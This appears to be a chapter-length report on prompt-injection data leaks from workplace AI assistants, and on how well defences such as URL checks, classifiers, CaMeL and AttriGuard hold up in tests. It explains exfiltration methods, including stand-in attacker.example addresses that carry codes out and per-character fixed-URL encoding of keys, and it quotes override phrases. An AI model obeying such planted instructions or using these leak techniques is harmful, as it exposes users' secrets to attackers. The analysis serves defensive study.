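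### Has the public web already seen this address?

OpenAI considers a list of trusted sites inadequate, partly because of redirects. It also warns that a strict list would produce so many false alarms that people would learn to click through them.

In January 2026, OpenAI described a different check for ChatGPT, in which it fetches a web address automatically only if OpenAI's crawler has already recorded that exact address. The crawler is a program that visits public web pages and records their addresses, and it has no access to users' conversations or accounts.

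Suppose an attacker plants a message telling ChatGPT to fetch `attacker.example/report?c=ABC-123`, where `ABC-123` is the employee's login code. The model has just composed this address, so the crawler won't have recorded it unless it was already public. If the address isn't recorded, ChatGPT tries another site or shows the employee a warning. It might still fetch `attacker.example/report` without the code, but the attacker would learn only that someone had requested the page.

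This test is better than checking a site's reputation because it also blocks new addresses on respectable sites. It would have stopped most of the leaks described so far if the products had applied it to every link and image.

Applying a check everywhere is hard. ChatGPT's earlier address check, from December 2023, was missing from its Mac and iPhone apps, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. Rehberger calls the new check a significant improvement, but warns that some of OpenAI's developers may not know to use it.

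### Spelling out a key with fixed addresses

The check examines each address separately, but an attacker can also learn something from the assistant's choice of addresses. The security company Radware demonstrated this against ChatGPT's connectors in September 2025.

OpenAI blocked an attack called ShadowLeak by stopping ChatGPT from adding anything to a web address, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. Radware then got around this by supplying complete addresses. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email containing one address for each letter and digit, and one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, it read the email and opened the addresses that spelled out the private data.

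To send a key that begins `k7f`, ChatGPT would open `attacker.example/k`, `attacker.example/7` and `attacker.example/f`. The attacker's log would then contain the start of the key, even though ChatGPT had opened each address exactly as supplied.

At one request per character, a 20-character key needs 20 requests. The attacker can use fewer if each address represents several characters. For a key made of lower-case letters and digits, there are 36^20 possible keys, so with N fixed addresses the attacker needs the smallest number of requests r for which

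N^r ≥ 36^20

| Fixed addresses | What each request reveals | Requests for a 20-character key |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | One bit | 104 |
| 36 | One character | 20 |
| 1,296 | Two characters | 10 |
| 46,656 | Three characters | 7 |

Rehberger suggests that an attacker could use thousands of addresses. The planted text would then have to give the model a much longer code, so the 36-address version seems the most practical for a single key.

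Many keys also contain capital letters. Radware converted its data to lower case, which does little harm to a name but corrupts a case-sensitive key. A random 20-character key of capitals, small letters and digits contains about 17 letters, so the attacker would have to try up to 2^17, or 131,072, combinations of capitals and small letters. Adding 26 addresses for the capitals would be easier.

Requests can also arrive in the wrong order, so Radware numbered the addresses by position: `k0` means a k in the first position and `k1` a k in the second. With 36 possible characters and ten positions per block, this takes 360 addresses. A 20-character key fills two blocks.

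Leaking a secret one character per request becomes less reliable as the secret gets longer. If each request succeeded 99% of the time, independently of the others, all 20 characters of a 20-character secret would arrive in about 82% of attempts. At 95% per request, this falls to 36%. In tests reported in *Silent Egress* (2026), splitting a secret across several requests could evade checks that examined requests one at a time, but it cut the rate of successful leaks by 73%.

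Radware nevertheless reported a 100% success rate for an improved version of its attack, without giving the number of attempts. An attacker may not need every character, because if one numbered character is missing, there are only 36 possibilities to try.

### Can OpenAI's check stop fixed addresses?

OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December 2025, 81 days after Radware's report. ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a public index or the user typed it, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. An attack that uses a list of addresses on a brand-new site would therefore fail.

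But an attacker may still be able to leak data through an established site. Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already. The planted message would only have to assign a character to each page. Rehberger also notes that OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this weakness.

Embrace The Red proposes stopping an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or storing each page for a few minutes so that a repeat visit sends no request. If an attacker leaks a key by making the agent visit one page per character, either measure would hide repeated characters. A random 20-character key of lower-case letters and digits contains about 15 or 16 different characters on average, so the attacker would lose four or five of the 20. The attacker could avoid this loss by using numbered addresses, with a separate set of pages for each position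 in the key, but would need 720 indexed pages (36 for each of the 20 positions).

OpenAI offers a stronger protection called Lockdown Mode, in which ChatGPT browses only stored copies of pages. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* says that no live browsing requests leave OpenAI's network. The attacker's server therefore receives no browsing request to log, whichever address the model tries to open.

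Lockdown Mode can leave search results stale or missing, and ChatGPT may not display images, according to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*. Planted instructions can still distort an answer. OpenAI says most users don't need this mode, but a company whose assistant reads both outside email and private messages has a good reason to consider it.

Anthropic's Claude had a similar weakness. Its page-opening tool accepted only addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that were linked from pages it had already opened. Willison (2026) describes how Ayush Paul exploited those links with a website that asked Claude to find the user's profile letter by letter. Each page offered links for the next letter, and by following them Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic, which said it had already found the problem internally, stopped the tool from following links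 on fetched pages.

Developers who build their own bots on Claude should be careful with this rule. In September 2025, Anthropic's API also accepted addresses in "user messages". As Willison noted, developers often put retrieved text in the same message as the employee's question. If that text included a message planted by an attacker, any address in it would count as one the user had supplied.

Some evidence suggests that ChatGPT's protections together help prevent leaks. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), the ChatGPT product leaked nothing in 48 valid trials, while a model reached through the programming interface leaked the secret up to 100% of the time. The researchers couldn't see inside the product, so it's unclear whether the address check was responsible.

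### The Atlassian Rovo setting that left a tool available

Rules for displaying links and images don't control an assistant that can open web pages itself. Administrators can turn off web search for the whole organisation in Rovo, the assistant in Atlassian products such as Jira and Confluence. Many would reasonably expect this to stop Rovo from contacting outside sites.

In August 2026, PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reported that it did not. In the demonstration:

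1. A user uploaded a document called "Backlog Guide" that contained hidden instructions.
2. The user asked Rovo to organise some Jira tickets.
3. Rovo searched Jira and Confluence, then added what it found to the attacker's address.
4. Rovo opened that address with its page-opening tool, and the attacker's server logged the data.

The setting had turned off search but left on the tool that opens search results. That tool had no rule against opening an address Rovo had just composed. Rovo did not ask for approval, and a user who reopened the chat later saw only sensible suggestions for the tickets.

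PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click, but The Hacker News (2026) disputes this because the victim has to give Rovo the poisoned file. PromptArmor's demonstration used an uploaded file. It says support tickets and connected services could also carry the instructions, which would require less action from the victim.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Atlassian on 23 May. Atlassian thanked PromptArmor and assigned a case number, but did not respond to follow-ups on 4 June and 29 July. PromptArmor published its findings on 5 August and said Rovo was still vulnerable. Three days later, The Hacker News could not confirm a fix and knew of no independent test of the web-search bypass.

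Varonis had separately found that a link could load instructions into Rovo's chat, and used an image address to steal an API key from Confluence. Atlassian fixed that flaw on 8 July. Neither company said in its disclosure whether the July fix affected PromptArmor's route.

Administrators can block Rovo for particular apps, and those on the Enterprise plan can also restrict it to certain groups. But if a site runs several Jira apps, Rovo's search and chat remain available until the administrator blocks Rovo for all of them.

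Google's Gemini filtered images and sent links through a Google address, but those protections did not apply to its browsing tool, according to Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool*. A planted instruction could make the tool send the user's saved information and location to an attacker without asking for confirmation. Google has since fixed the flaw.

### Google's and Microsoft's published rules

Google says Gemini identifies external image URLs and doesn't display the images, so EchoLeak's image-based leak doesn't apply to it. Google doesn't define "external", however, and Superhuman's experience with Google Forms suggests that an exception for Google's own domains would be risky.

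Gemini removes suspicious links from its answers and checks files for them before it processes a request. If it excludes some of the material, it tells the user that it did so for security reasons.

*Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes a central system that holds Google's rules for links, confirmations and combinations of tools. The rules on combinations can cover tools that are harmless alone but dangerous together, such as one that reads email and one that opens web pages. Google can change these rules faster than it can retrain a model. Its quick fixes include blocking text that matches a known pattern, though an attacker may get around this by rewording the text.

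Microsoft's published rules are less specific. Microsoft says it blocked image leaks and "certain untrusted links" after Rehberger reported an image leak, but it doesn't say which links. It also says it looks for variants whenever it fixes a reported flaw, which is hard to reconcile with the image leaks through Bing in 2026. Checkmarx, which sells software security products, says Microsoft did not commit to fixing an image leak Checkmarx had demonstrated in Copilot Chat, because Microsoft did not consider it a vulnerability.

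Google and Microsoft also ask for confirmation before some actions. Gemini asks before deleting calendar events, and Copilot in Outlook can draft an email, but the user has to approve and send it. This works well for occasional actions that the user understands. It would be a poor way to control images or page requests, because an assistant may make dozens in one task. SafeBreach also got around Gemini's confirmation by asking the question in a language the user couldn't read.

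### Which measures stop which requests?

A bot that posts in Slack and opens web pages needs separate protection for each activity, because turning off link previews does not restrict the tool it uses to open pages. The table assumes that an attacker already controls the model through a planted message and that each measure works as designed.

| Measure | Clicked link | Image in an answer | Link preview | Tool request |
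|---|---|---|---|---|
| Remove all outside links | Stops it | No effect | Stops it if removal comes before posting | No effect |
| Show the full address and ask | Depends on the user | Impractical | No effect after posting | Depends on the user |
| Remove invisible characters | Stops hidden data only | Stops hidden data only | Stops hidden data only | Only if applied to the request |
| Load no outside images | No effect | Stops it | No effect | No effect |
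| Turn off previews for bot messages | No effect | No effect | Stops it | No effect |
| Allow only listed sites | Relays can defeat it | Relays can defeat it | Only if applied before posting | Relays can defeat it |
| Allow only publicly known addresses | Warns about new addresses | Fixed addresses can defeat it | Only if applied before posting | Fixed addresses can defeat it |
| Browse only stored pages | No effect | No effect without a separate image rule | No effect | Stops live browsing, but not other tools |

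## How well do defences against planted instructions hold up in tests?

Blocking links and images limits the damage after a model follows planted instructions. Other defences try to stop the model from following them. Researchers usually test these defences by giving an assistant ordinary work in a simulated office, planting instructions in what it reads, and counting how often it carries them out.

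### AgentDojo's simulated Slack workspace

Many of these tests use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), the suite on which Microsoft's researchers also tried FIDES. Its Slack workspace has 11 tools, 21 user tasks and 5 injected tasks, which are the attacker's goals. Nine of the tools read and send messages or manage channels and members, and the other two read and post web pages.

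In one user task, an employee asks the agent to invite Dora to Slack and says her email address is on her website. In one injected task, the attacker wants the agent to send Alice a phishing link. The attacker's instructions are in web pages that the agent reads. Pairing every user task with every injected task gives 105 combinations.

After each run, ordinary code checks the workspace to see whether the agent invited Dora and whether Alice received the link. Debenedetti and colleagues chose not to use a language model as the judge, because the planted text might fool it too. According to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), AgentDojo also runs each injected task by itself, as if the user had asked for it. This shows whether the model can do what the attacker wants. A weak model can look safe because it fails at most tasks. In 2024, attacks succeeded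 against Cohere's Command R+ only 1% of the time, but it completed only 25% of the ordinary tasks.

OpenAI's GPT-4o, one of the best models in that test, carried out the attacker's task in 92% of the Slack cases, compared with 48% across all four simulated settings. Debenedetti and colleagues suggest that the rate was higher in Slack because the attacker had written much of the text the agent read there. Across all settings, a blunt command to ignore earlier instructions worked about 5% of the time, while a message made to look as if it came from the user worked 58% of the time.

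Newer models do much better on AgentDojo. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) found that GPT-5.5 completed 88.7% of its ordinary tasks, up from 69% for GPT-4o in 2024. They also attacked five models in a version of AgentDojo that divides the work among several agents. Without added defences, attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1, 1.5% against Claude Fable 5 and never against GPT-5.5.

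AgentDojo is a better guide to agents that post messages than to assistants that only answer questions. In its Slack tests, the attacks come from web pages, and the attacker typically wants the agent to do something, such as send a message to a user named Alice. In the Slack AI leak, the planted text was a Slack message, and the assistant only had to include a link in its answer.

### Classifiers that screen incoming text

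A classifier, which Copilot also uses, is usually a small model separate from the main one. If it flags retrieved text, the assistant can discard the text or stop. Developers like classifiers because they can add one without changing the main model.

He, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *AttriGuard*, compared 13 existing defences with one of their own, so they had an interest in finding weaknesses in the others. Their test was thorough, however. It used 882 combinations of user task and attack from AgentDojo, each with four different wordings. These are some of the results with Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash:

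| Defence | Ordinary tasks completed, no attack | Attack success, "ignore previous instructions" wording | Attack success, text posing as the user |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 57.6% | 1.5% | 33.0% |
| PromptGuard | 40.2% | 1.4% | 19.8% |
| PIGuard | 34.8% | 0.2% | 1.4% |

The PIGuard classifier stopped nearly all the attacks, but it also flagged harmless text, so the assistant completed far fewer ordinary tasks. PromptGuard interfered less with those tasks but let many more attacks through. A company could adjust a classifier's sensitivity, but catching more attacks would also mean flagging more harmless text.

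The table also shows why a developer should not test a classifier only with well-known attacks. Gemini already ignored the well-known wording almost every time, so any classifier would have seemed excellent in a test that used only that wording.

### Marking retrieved text, or training the model to distrust it

Another approach is to help the main model tell data from instructions. The easiest way to do this is to change the prompt. In spotlighting, the developer puts marks around text to show which parts the model should trust. Another method, "prompt sandwiching", repeats the user's request after the retrieved text to keep the model focused on that request.

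Spotlighting and sandwiching had little effect in tests by He and colleagues. When the planted text was written as if it came from the user, attacks on Gemini succeeded 33.0% of the time without a defence, 34.8% with spotlighting and 28.3% with sandwiching.

Training a model to ignore planted instructions works better than marking. Meta SecAlign is a version of Meta's Llama 3.3 70B model that researchers trained on examples containing such instructions. In the same test, this training reduced attack success from 22.1% to 0.8% and raised the share of ordinary tasks completed from 59.8% to 78.3%. He et al. attribute most of the improvement on ordinary tasks to formatting. The original model often left out a closing bracket when it called a tool, and the training happened to fix this.

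A company can choose a model with such training, but it can't easily add it to a commercial model it rents. The company also has no simple way to check whether the model learned to distrust retrieved text in general or only text that resembles the training examples.

### What happens when the attacker adapts?

The tests above fixed the attacker's wording in advance, but a real attacker can change the wording and try again. The change can make a large difference. When Yang and colleagues tried two kinds of planted text on a ChatGPT-based chatbot, one succeeded in 4 of 136 attempts and the other in 121 of 168.

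Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, attacked 12 published defences this way. Most were meant to stop planted instructions, though some were meant to stop users from extracting harmful information. Their automated search generated attack texts, tried them on the defended system, scored the results and used the best texts to write the next batch. The researchers also ran an online contest in which more than 500 people tried to break defences by hand.

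| Defence | Type | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marking | Above 95% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Marking | Above 95% |
| Meta SecAlign | Training | 96% |
| PromptGuard | Classifier | Above 90% |
| Google's Model Armor | Classifier | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Classifier | 71% |

AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against the two marking methods and 2% against Meta SecAlign. On a selected set of cases, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, and at least one human contestant succeeded in every case.

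Many of the successful texts contained no obvious attack. They presented the attacker's task as a company rule or as a step the agent had to finish before doing what the user wanted. EchoLeak's email got past Microsoft's classifier in much the same way.

These rates are close to a worst case, because the search against the classifiers used each classifier's confidence score after every attempt. A stranger who emails an employee can't see those scores, but can often buy the same product and practise on it, as Cato's researchers did with Copilot.

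The results also depend on how hard the attacker tries. He and colleagues adapted the same search, allowed it 200 tries per case, and broke Meta SecAlign in 24.6% of 61 cases, far below the 96% that Nasr and colleagues reported. The gap may come from the limit on tries, the choice of cases or a less effective search. Either way, tests with fixed attacks had made the defence look much stronger than it was.

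Nasr and colleagues still consider classifiers useful for blocking unsophisticated attacks. This seems right for a workplace assistant, as long as the company does not rely on the classifier to protect a password to its customer database.

### CaMeL fixes the plan before reading anything

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, keeps planted text away from the model that chooses the actions, so the attacker's wording can't influence that model. Like FIDES, it uses one model to plan and another to read untrusted text, an arrangement Willison had proposed earlier.

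Suppose an employee gives a CaMeL agent the task about Dora:

1. The planning model sees only the employee's request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a short program that reads Dora's web page, extracts her email address and invites her to Slack.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. It fetches the page and stores the text without showing it to the planning model.
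3. A "quarantined" model, which has no tools, reads the page and returns the address.
4. The interpreter labels the address with its source and the people who may read it. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which proposes an extension of CaMeL, calls these labels capabilities.
5. Before the interpreter sends the invitation, it checks the address and its labels against a security policy, which allows or denies the action.

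If Dora's page also contains an instruction to send Alice a phishing link, only the quarantined model reads it, and that model can't send messages. The program has no step that contacts Alice, so the attack fails however persuasive the text is.

The attacker can still give their own address as Dora's on the page, and the program will then invite the attacker to the workspace. Only the policy in step 5 can prevent this, and a suitable rule is hard to write. A ban on inviting addresses found on web pages would stop the attack, but also the task the employee asked for. The policy could instead require the employee to confirm the address.

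Like the tested version of FIDES, CaMeL would need an extra check on displayed answers to prevent the Slack AI leak, because it applies its policy when the program calls a tool. The quarantined model would read both the key and the planted message, so it could still write a link containing the key.

He and colleagues found that none of their fixed attacks succeeded against CaMeL, with any of the four wordings. The cost was considerable:

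| | No defence | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Attack success, text posing as the user | 33.0% | 0.0% |
| Ordinary tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 57.6% | 38.0% |
| Ordinary tasks completed, Llama 3.3 70B | 59.8% | 37.0% |
| Average time per task under attack, Gemini | 11 seconds | 165 seconds |

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) is more favourable, reporting that CaMeL eliminates nearly all AgentDojo attacks "while maintaining comparable task performance". The choice of model probably explains part of the disagreement. CaMeL requires a model to write a correct program before seeing any of the data, which is difficult for a small model such as Gemini 2.5 Flash.

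CaMeL and FIDES both perform poorly when an employee asks them to read a message and follow whatever instructions it contains. These failures have little to do with the model's skill.

Neither Nasr and colleagues nor He and colleagues ran their adaptive attacks on CaMeL. Several of the researchers who broke the 12 other defences had also helped to design CaMeL, so they had a reason to favour its approach. The argument for CaMeL also relies on its design. The planning model writes a program without reading the planted message, so rewording the message can't add a step to the program, provided the interpreter has no faults.

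### When one protected agent instructs another

Companies increasingly divide work among several agents. One agent might take the employee's request and pass parts of it to a second that searches a database and a third that posts in Slack. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that giving each agent its own copy of CaMeL leaves a gap between the agents.

In one demonstration, a user asked a lead agent to send Julie a summary of some job applicants on Slack. The applicant database contained a planted instruction to email the data to an outside address. The database agent and the lead agent followed their original plans, but the lead agent included the planted instruction with the summary in its request to the notification agent. The notification agent's planning model treated the whole request as coming from its user, so the agent sent Julie the summary and emailed the same data to the attacker.

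The researchers call this "boundary laundering", because untrusted text becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to another. Their fix, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into a generic instruction, such as "send the recipient the provided content", and stored values that hold the name and summary. The receiving planning model can't read those values, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that contains text from a tool.

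To test it, they split AgentDojo's tools among specialised agents. In the Slack workspace, one agent handled messages and channels while another handled web pages. They ran 949 attacks on each model in each configuration:

| Model | No CaMeL | Separate CaMeL agents | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
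| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

The 0.2% amounts to about nine successes in 4,745 attacks. In all of them, the planted instruction passed from one agent to another, as in the demonstration. In one Slack task, the user asked for feedback on Dora's and Eve's websites. One site contained an instruction to send someone a malicious link, and the lead agent copied that instruction into its request to the Slack agent.

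These results concern only the plan. The researchers ran CaMeL without security policies, so the test didn't measure whether an attacker could misuse a planned step, for instance by changing an address. They also acknowledge that CaMeL's interpreter can miss some indirect ways untrusted text affects a value, and that multi-CaMeL has the same fault.

On AssetOpsBench, a separate test of industrial maintenance work, giving each agent its own CaMeL reduced task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, CaMeL reduced completion by 13.4 points and multi-CaMeL by less than one more. A company that already uses CaMeL with a strong model can therefore add protection between agents with little further loss in task completion.

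Multi-CaMeL assumes a strict hierarchy in which each agent takes instructions from only one other agent. Bots that read and answer each other's posts in a Slack channel don't follow such a hierarchy. The channel mixes employees' requests, retrieved text and other bots' replies in one stream. Extending the protection to this setting is still an open problem.

### AttriGuard asks what caused each action

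CaMeL loses flexibility because it plans without seeing the data. AttriGuard, a defence from He and colleagues, lets the model read everything and checks each action before it happens. The idea is that an employee's request should be enough to prompt a legitimate action, whereas an attacker's action depends on the model treating the planted text as a command.

Take Dora's page again, with the instruction to send Alice a link. After reading it, the agent proposes to invite Dora and to message Alice. AttriGuard then does the following:

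1. It has a language model rewrite the page so that commands become reports. An order to send Alice a link becomes a statement that, according to the page, someone should send Alice a link.
2. It gives the agent the same request and the same history, with the rewritten page in place of the original.
3. It compares the two sets of proposed actions. If the agent again wants to invite Dora, that action goes ahead.
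4. If the message to Alice has disappeared, AttriGuard blocks it and tells the agent to continue with the user's task.

When the tool is the same but the details differ, another language model checks whether the action still fits the request, since a model may word a harmless message differently each time.

Most of AttriGuard's protection comes from rewriting the text. In a test with GPT-4.1-mini, it let 12.2% of attacks through when it only turned structured data into plain sentences, and none when it also turned commands into reports. An agent working from the rewritten text alone completed 61.8% of ordinary tasks instead of 70.6%, because rewriting loses details.

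In the main comparison, AttriGuard stopped every fixed attack on Gemini 2.5 Flash and Llama 3.3 70B. With AttriGuard, Gemini completed 67.4% of ordinary tasks and Llama completed 54.4%, much more than with CaMeL. Tasks took about three times as long as without a defence.

He and colleagues then attacked AttriGuard with the adaptive search, which received a description of the defence and information about what it had blocked:

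| Defence | Success of adaptive attacks, Gemini | Success of adaptive attacks, Llama |
|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 52.5% | 55.7% |
| MELON | 82.0% | Not tested |
| Meta SecAlign | Not tested | 24.6% |
| AttriGuard | 6.6% | 9.8% |

Raising the limit from 200 tries to 500 did not increase the 6.6% success rate. But that is only 4 successes in 61 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 3% to 16%. The researchers also attacked their own defence, and an outside team might find a better way to break it.

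MELON's test results are a reason for caution. It also runs the agent twice, but in the second run it replaces the user's request with a neutral one and checks for actions that still occur. It stopped nearly all fixed attacks on Gemini, but Nasr and colleagues broke it 76% of the time using a search that had no information about how it worked, and 95% of the time when the search included that information.

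The test also left out attacks that succeed through the answer's text alone. AttriGuard examines tool calls but does not check the final answer. It could stop a planted message from making an agent post in a channel, but it would miss a leak like the one from Slack AI.

### What do the developers' own tests show?

AI developers publish the results of prompt injection tests in system cards, the safety reports that accompany new models. These results are more recent than most academic ones, and the attacks are often stronger, but the developers are testing their own products.

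Anthropic's test results for Claude Opus 4.6 in February 2026 varied widely with the task. VentureBeat reports that no attack succeeded in 200 attempts in a restricted programming setting. When the model operated a computer through its screen, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, the rate had reached 78.6% without extra safeguards and 57.1% with them.

Later Claude models appear more resistant. In programming tests with 200 attempts per scenario, adaptive attacks had a success rate of 0.41% against Fable 5 and 2.09% against Opus 4.8, according to Digital Applied (2026), an agency that reviewed the June system card. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1, published in September, describes Mythos 5.1 as the company's most robust model so far on an outside test of indirect prompt injection. The card gives separate results for programming,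 computer use and web browsing, but none of these closely resembles answering a question from a company's Slack messages, so the best figure may not hold for a workplace assistant.

OpenAI distinguishes direct attacks, which a user types, from indirect attacks, which are planted in material that the model retrieves. GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of the direct attacks in an August 2026 update, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*. Indirect attacks can arrive in emails, files or web pages, and are the relevant kind for a workplace assistant. Their average success rate was 3.77% against Sol and 2.94% against Luna, the most resistant of the three GPT-5.6 models.

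They also suggest that GPT-5.5 scored perfectly on AgentDojo because the benchmark's attacks, which date from 2024, have become too easy. Developers have perhaps since trained their models on similar texts. This explanation is more likely than GPT-5.5 being immune when its successor was not. A caution in OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) about a different set of safety tests also applies here: "the absence of observed failures does not establish reliability across settings".

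Peters-Gill and colleagues, working outside Google, measured 24.6% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, an older Google model. This figure can't be compared directly with OpenAI's or Anthropic's, because each test used different attacks.

### Why a 1% success rate can still be too high

An attacker can send more than one email. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of n attempts succeeds is

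1 − (1 − p)^n

With a success rate of 1% and 200 attempts, this is 1 − 0.99^200, or about 87%.

| Success rate per attempt | 20 attempts | 200 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| 0.1% | 2% | 18% |
| 1% | 18% | 87% |
| 3.77% | 54% | More than 99.9% |

An attempt here means that the model has read the planted text, so an email that the assistant never retrieves doesn't count. Even a successful attempt leaks nothing if the company has blocked every way for data to get out. But an attacker who sends one email to 200 employees could get 200 attempts from it.

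Repeated attempts at an attack are often not independent. Suppose a model has a 1% failure rate because one type of request in a hundred always fools it and the others never do. An attack using any other type would then fail even after 200 attempts. The results for Opus 4.6 show a milder version of this. If each attempt had independently had a 17.8% chance of success, about 98% of attacks would have succeeded within 20 attempts. But 21.4% had still failed after 200, so some scenarios must have been much harder than others.

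The formula can also underestimate the danger. An attacker who learns from each failure is more likely to succeed on the next attempt, which is how the adaptive searches broke defences that had looked nearly perfect. And if 200 employees use the same assistant, a planted instruction that works in one employee's session may work in many others on the same day.

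## Have attackers used these methods, and how would an organisation notice?

Researchers carried out the attacks on Slack AI, Copilot and Rovo described so far. None of the companies involved has reported a real theft by these methods.

Some headlines present research on these methods as real attacks. Two days after Cato published ReLeak, *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) described a "new ReLeak campaign" that "looks to steal data from victims". In security writing, a campaign usually means a series of real attacks by one group, but these hackers were Cato's own researchers. *Attackers tricked Copilot into leaking sensitive data through Bing* (Okemwa, 2026) similarly presented SearchLeak as the work of attackers in June, although the article's summary credits researchers. Anyone who counts incidents by their headlines would therefore count two that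 nobody has reported.

### What did the companies say about real attacks?

| Attack | Source of the statement | Statement |
|---|---|---|
| Slack AI, 2024 | Slack | No evidence "at this time" of unauthorised access to customer data |
| EchoLeak, 2025 | Microsoft | No exploitation, or no evidence of it |
| SearchLeak, 2026 | Thailand's computer emergency team | No reports of active exploitation |
| ReLeak, 2026 | Cato | No known affected customers |

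Reports differ on how firmly exploitation of EchoLeak and ReLeak has been ruled out, and in both cases the weaker claim is easier to believe. On EchoLeak, SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports that Microsoft said nobody had exploited the flaw, while SiliconANGLE reports only that Microsoft had found no evidence of exploitation. On ReLeak, the summary above Faisal's article says that Microsoft ruled out any affected customers, but the article itself says that Cato knew of none.

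The SearchLeak statement in ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* summarises a news report, so it is weak evidence of what Microsoft found in its own records. OECD's *Slack AI Vulnerability Exposes Private Channel Data* classes the Slack flaw as a plausible future harm because Slack repaired it before anyone documented damage. The category is sensible, but the entry is AI-generated and adds no separate evidence.

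### What can "no known exploitation" show?

It depends on how likely the search was to find a theft. Let p be the probability, before anyone looks, that a theft happened, and d the chance that the search would find it. If the search finds nothing, the probability that a theft happened is

p(1 − d) / (p(1 − d) + 1 − p)

Suppose p is 10%. A search that finds nothing lowers it to about 1% if the search would catch nine thefts in ten, but only to about 8% if it would catch two in ten.

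Microsoft's own search for attacks could have been effective, because its servers passed on the data in EchoLeak and SearchLeak. Once it knew the method, it could check its records for image requests that contained an outside address. But its brief statements don't describe the search or how far back it went. Slack issued its statement a week after PromptArmor's first report and a day after deploying the fix, which left little time for a thorough investigation.

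Customers can check less. Microsoft says that the hunting tool for security teams in its Defender service can search up to 30 days of raw data. A company that first heard of ReLeak on 3 December could therefore look back to 3 November. That covers the last 12 days before Microsoft repaired the image route and the last eight before it repaired the file route, but none of the time when the code interpreter was vulnerable, because Microsoft repaired that on 17 September. A company that exports its logs to longer storage can look back further, provided the logs recorded the relevant activity.

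### Planted text outside the laboratory

People plant instructions for AI in real web pages and emails. In April 2026, Google published the results of a search of Common Crawl, a web archive with monthly snapshots of two to three billion pages each. Google searched for familiar phrases such as "if you are an AI", used Gemini to assess the purpose of the suspicious text, and had people check the results.

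Most of the planted text was pranks, guidance for AI summaries, product promotion or attempts to keep AI agents away. A few pages tried to steal data, but the example Google gave was a website author's experiment. Google found no significant number of attacks using the methods that researchers had published in 2025. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, which also covers a search by the security company Forcepoint, lists API keys among the targets.

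Google found 32% more malicious text in February 2026 than in November 2025. It doesn't say how many pages that was, so the rise could be small in absolute terms. The archive it searched doesn't contain private email or Slack messages, and a search for familiar phrases would miss an email like EchoLeak's, which never mentioned AI.

The closest thing to real use of these methods against workplace assistants is advertising. Over 60 days, Microsoft found about 50 different prompts from 31 companies, including a security vendor, in links sent by email. The links were often attached to a "Summarize with AI" button. Clicking one opened an assistant with a prompt already filled in, much as SearchLeak did, with an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source.

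Some of those links led to Copilot, ChatGPT and Claude, which people also use at work. Microsoft doesn't report how many employees clicked, or whether any workplace assistant saved the instruction. The companies wanted recommendations rather than passwords, but their links show that putting instructions in a web address is already easy and common.

Phishers have also used invisible tag characters to get past spam filters, and this can trigger rules meant to detect hidden AI instructions. Microsoft (2026) had written such a rule for email. It matched about 21,000 messages on 8 February 2026 and more than 1.3 million the next day. The phishers had put an invisible character inside words such as "funding" so that spam filters would not recognise them. The messages Microsoft sampled contained no instructions to an AI. A company that counted every match as an attack on its assistant would have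 greatly overestimated the number of attacks.

None of these reports describes planted text that made a workplace assistant leak a secret. Google suggests that attackers have so far found the method exotic and unreliable, and expects this to change as assistants become more capable. Thieves have also had easier ways to get the same data.

### Disney's messages and the Drift tokens

In 2024, a California man named Ryan Kramer published malware disguised as a tool for making AI art. A Disney employee downloaded it, giving Kramer access to the employee's computer and stored passwords. Kramer used the employee's Slack account to download about 1.1 terabytes of data from thousands of channels, and released it that July. He later pleaded guilty.

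Kramer could sign in as the employee, so he didn't need to trick an assistant. The theft shows how much someone can read through one ordinary account. A workplace assistant that searches with the same permissions can reach much of the same material, though an attacker using a planted message would have to extract it a little at a time.

Drift, sold by Salesloft, is a chat agent that companies put on their websites. Many customers had connected it to Salesforce, where they keep sales and support records. In August 2025, thieves stole the tokens for those connections and used them to copy records from more than 700 organisations. They then searched the copies for passwords and for keys to cloud services.

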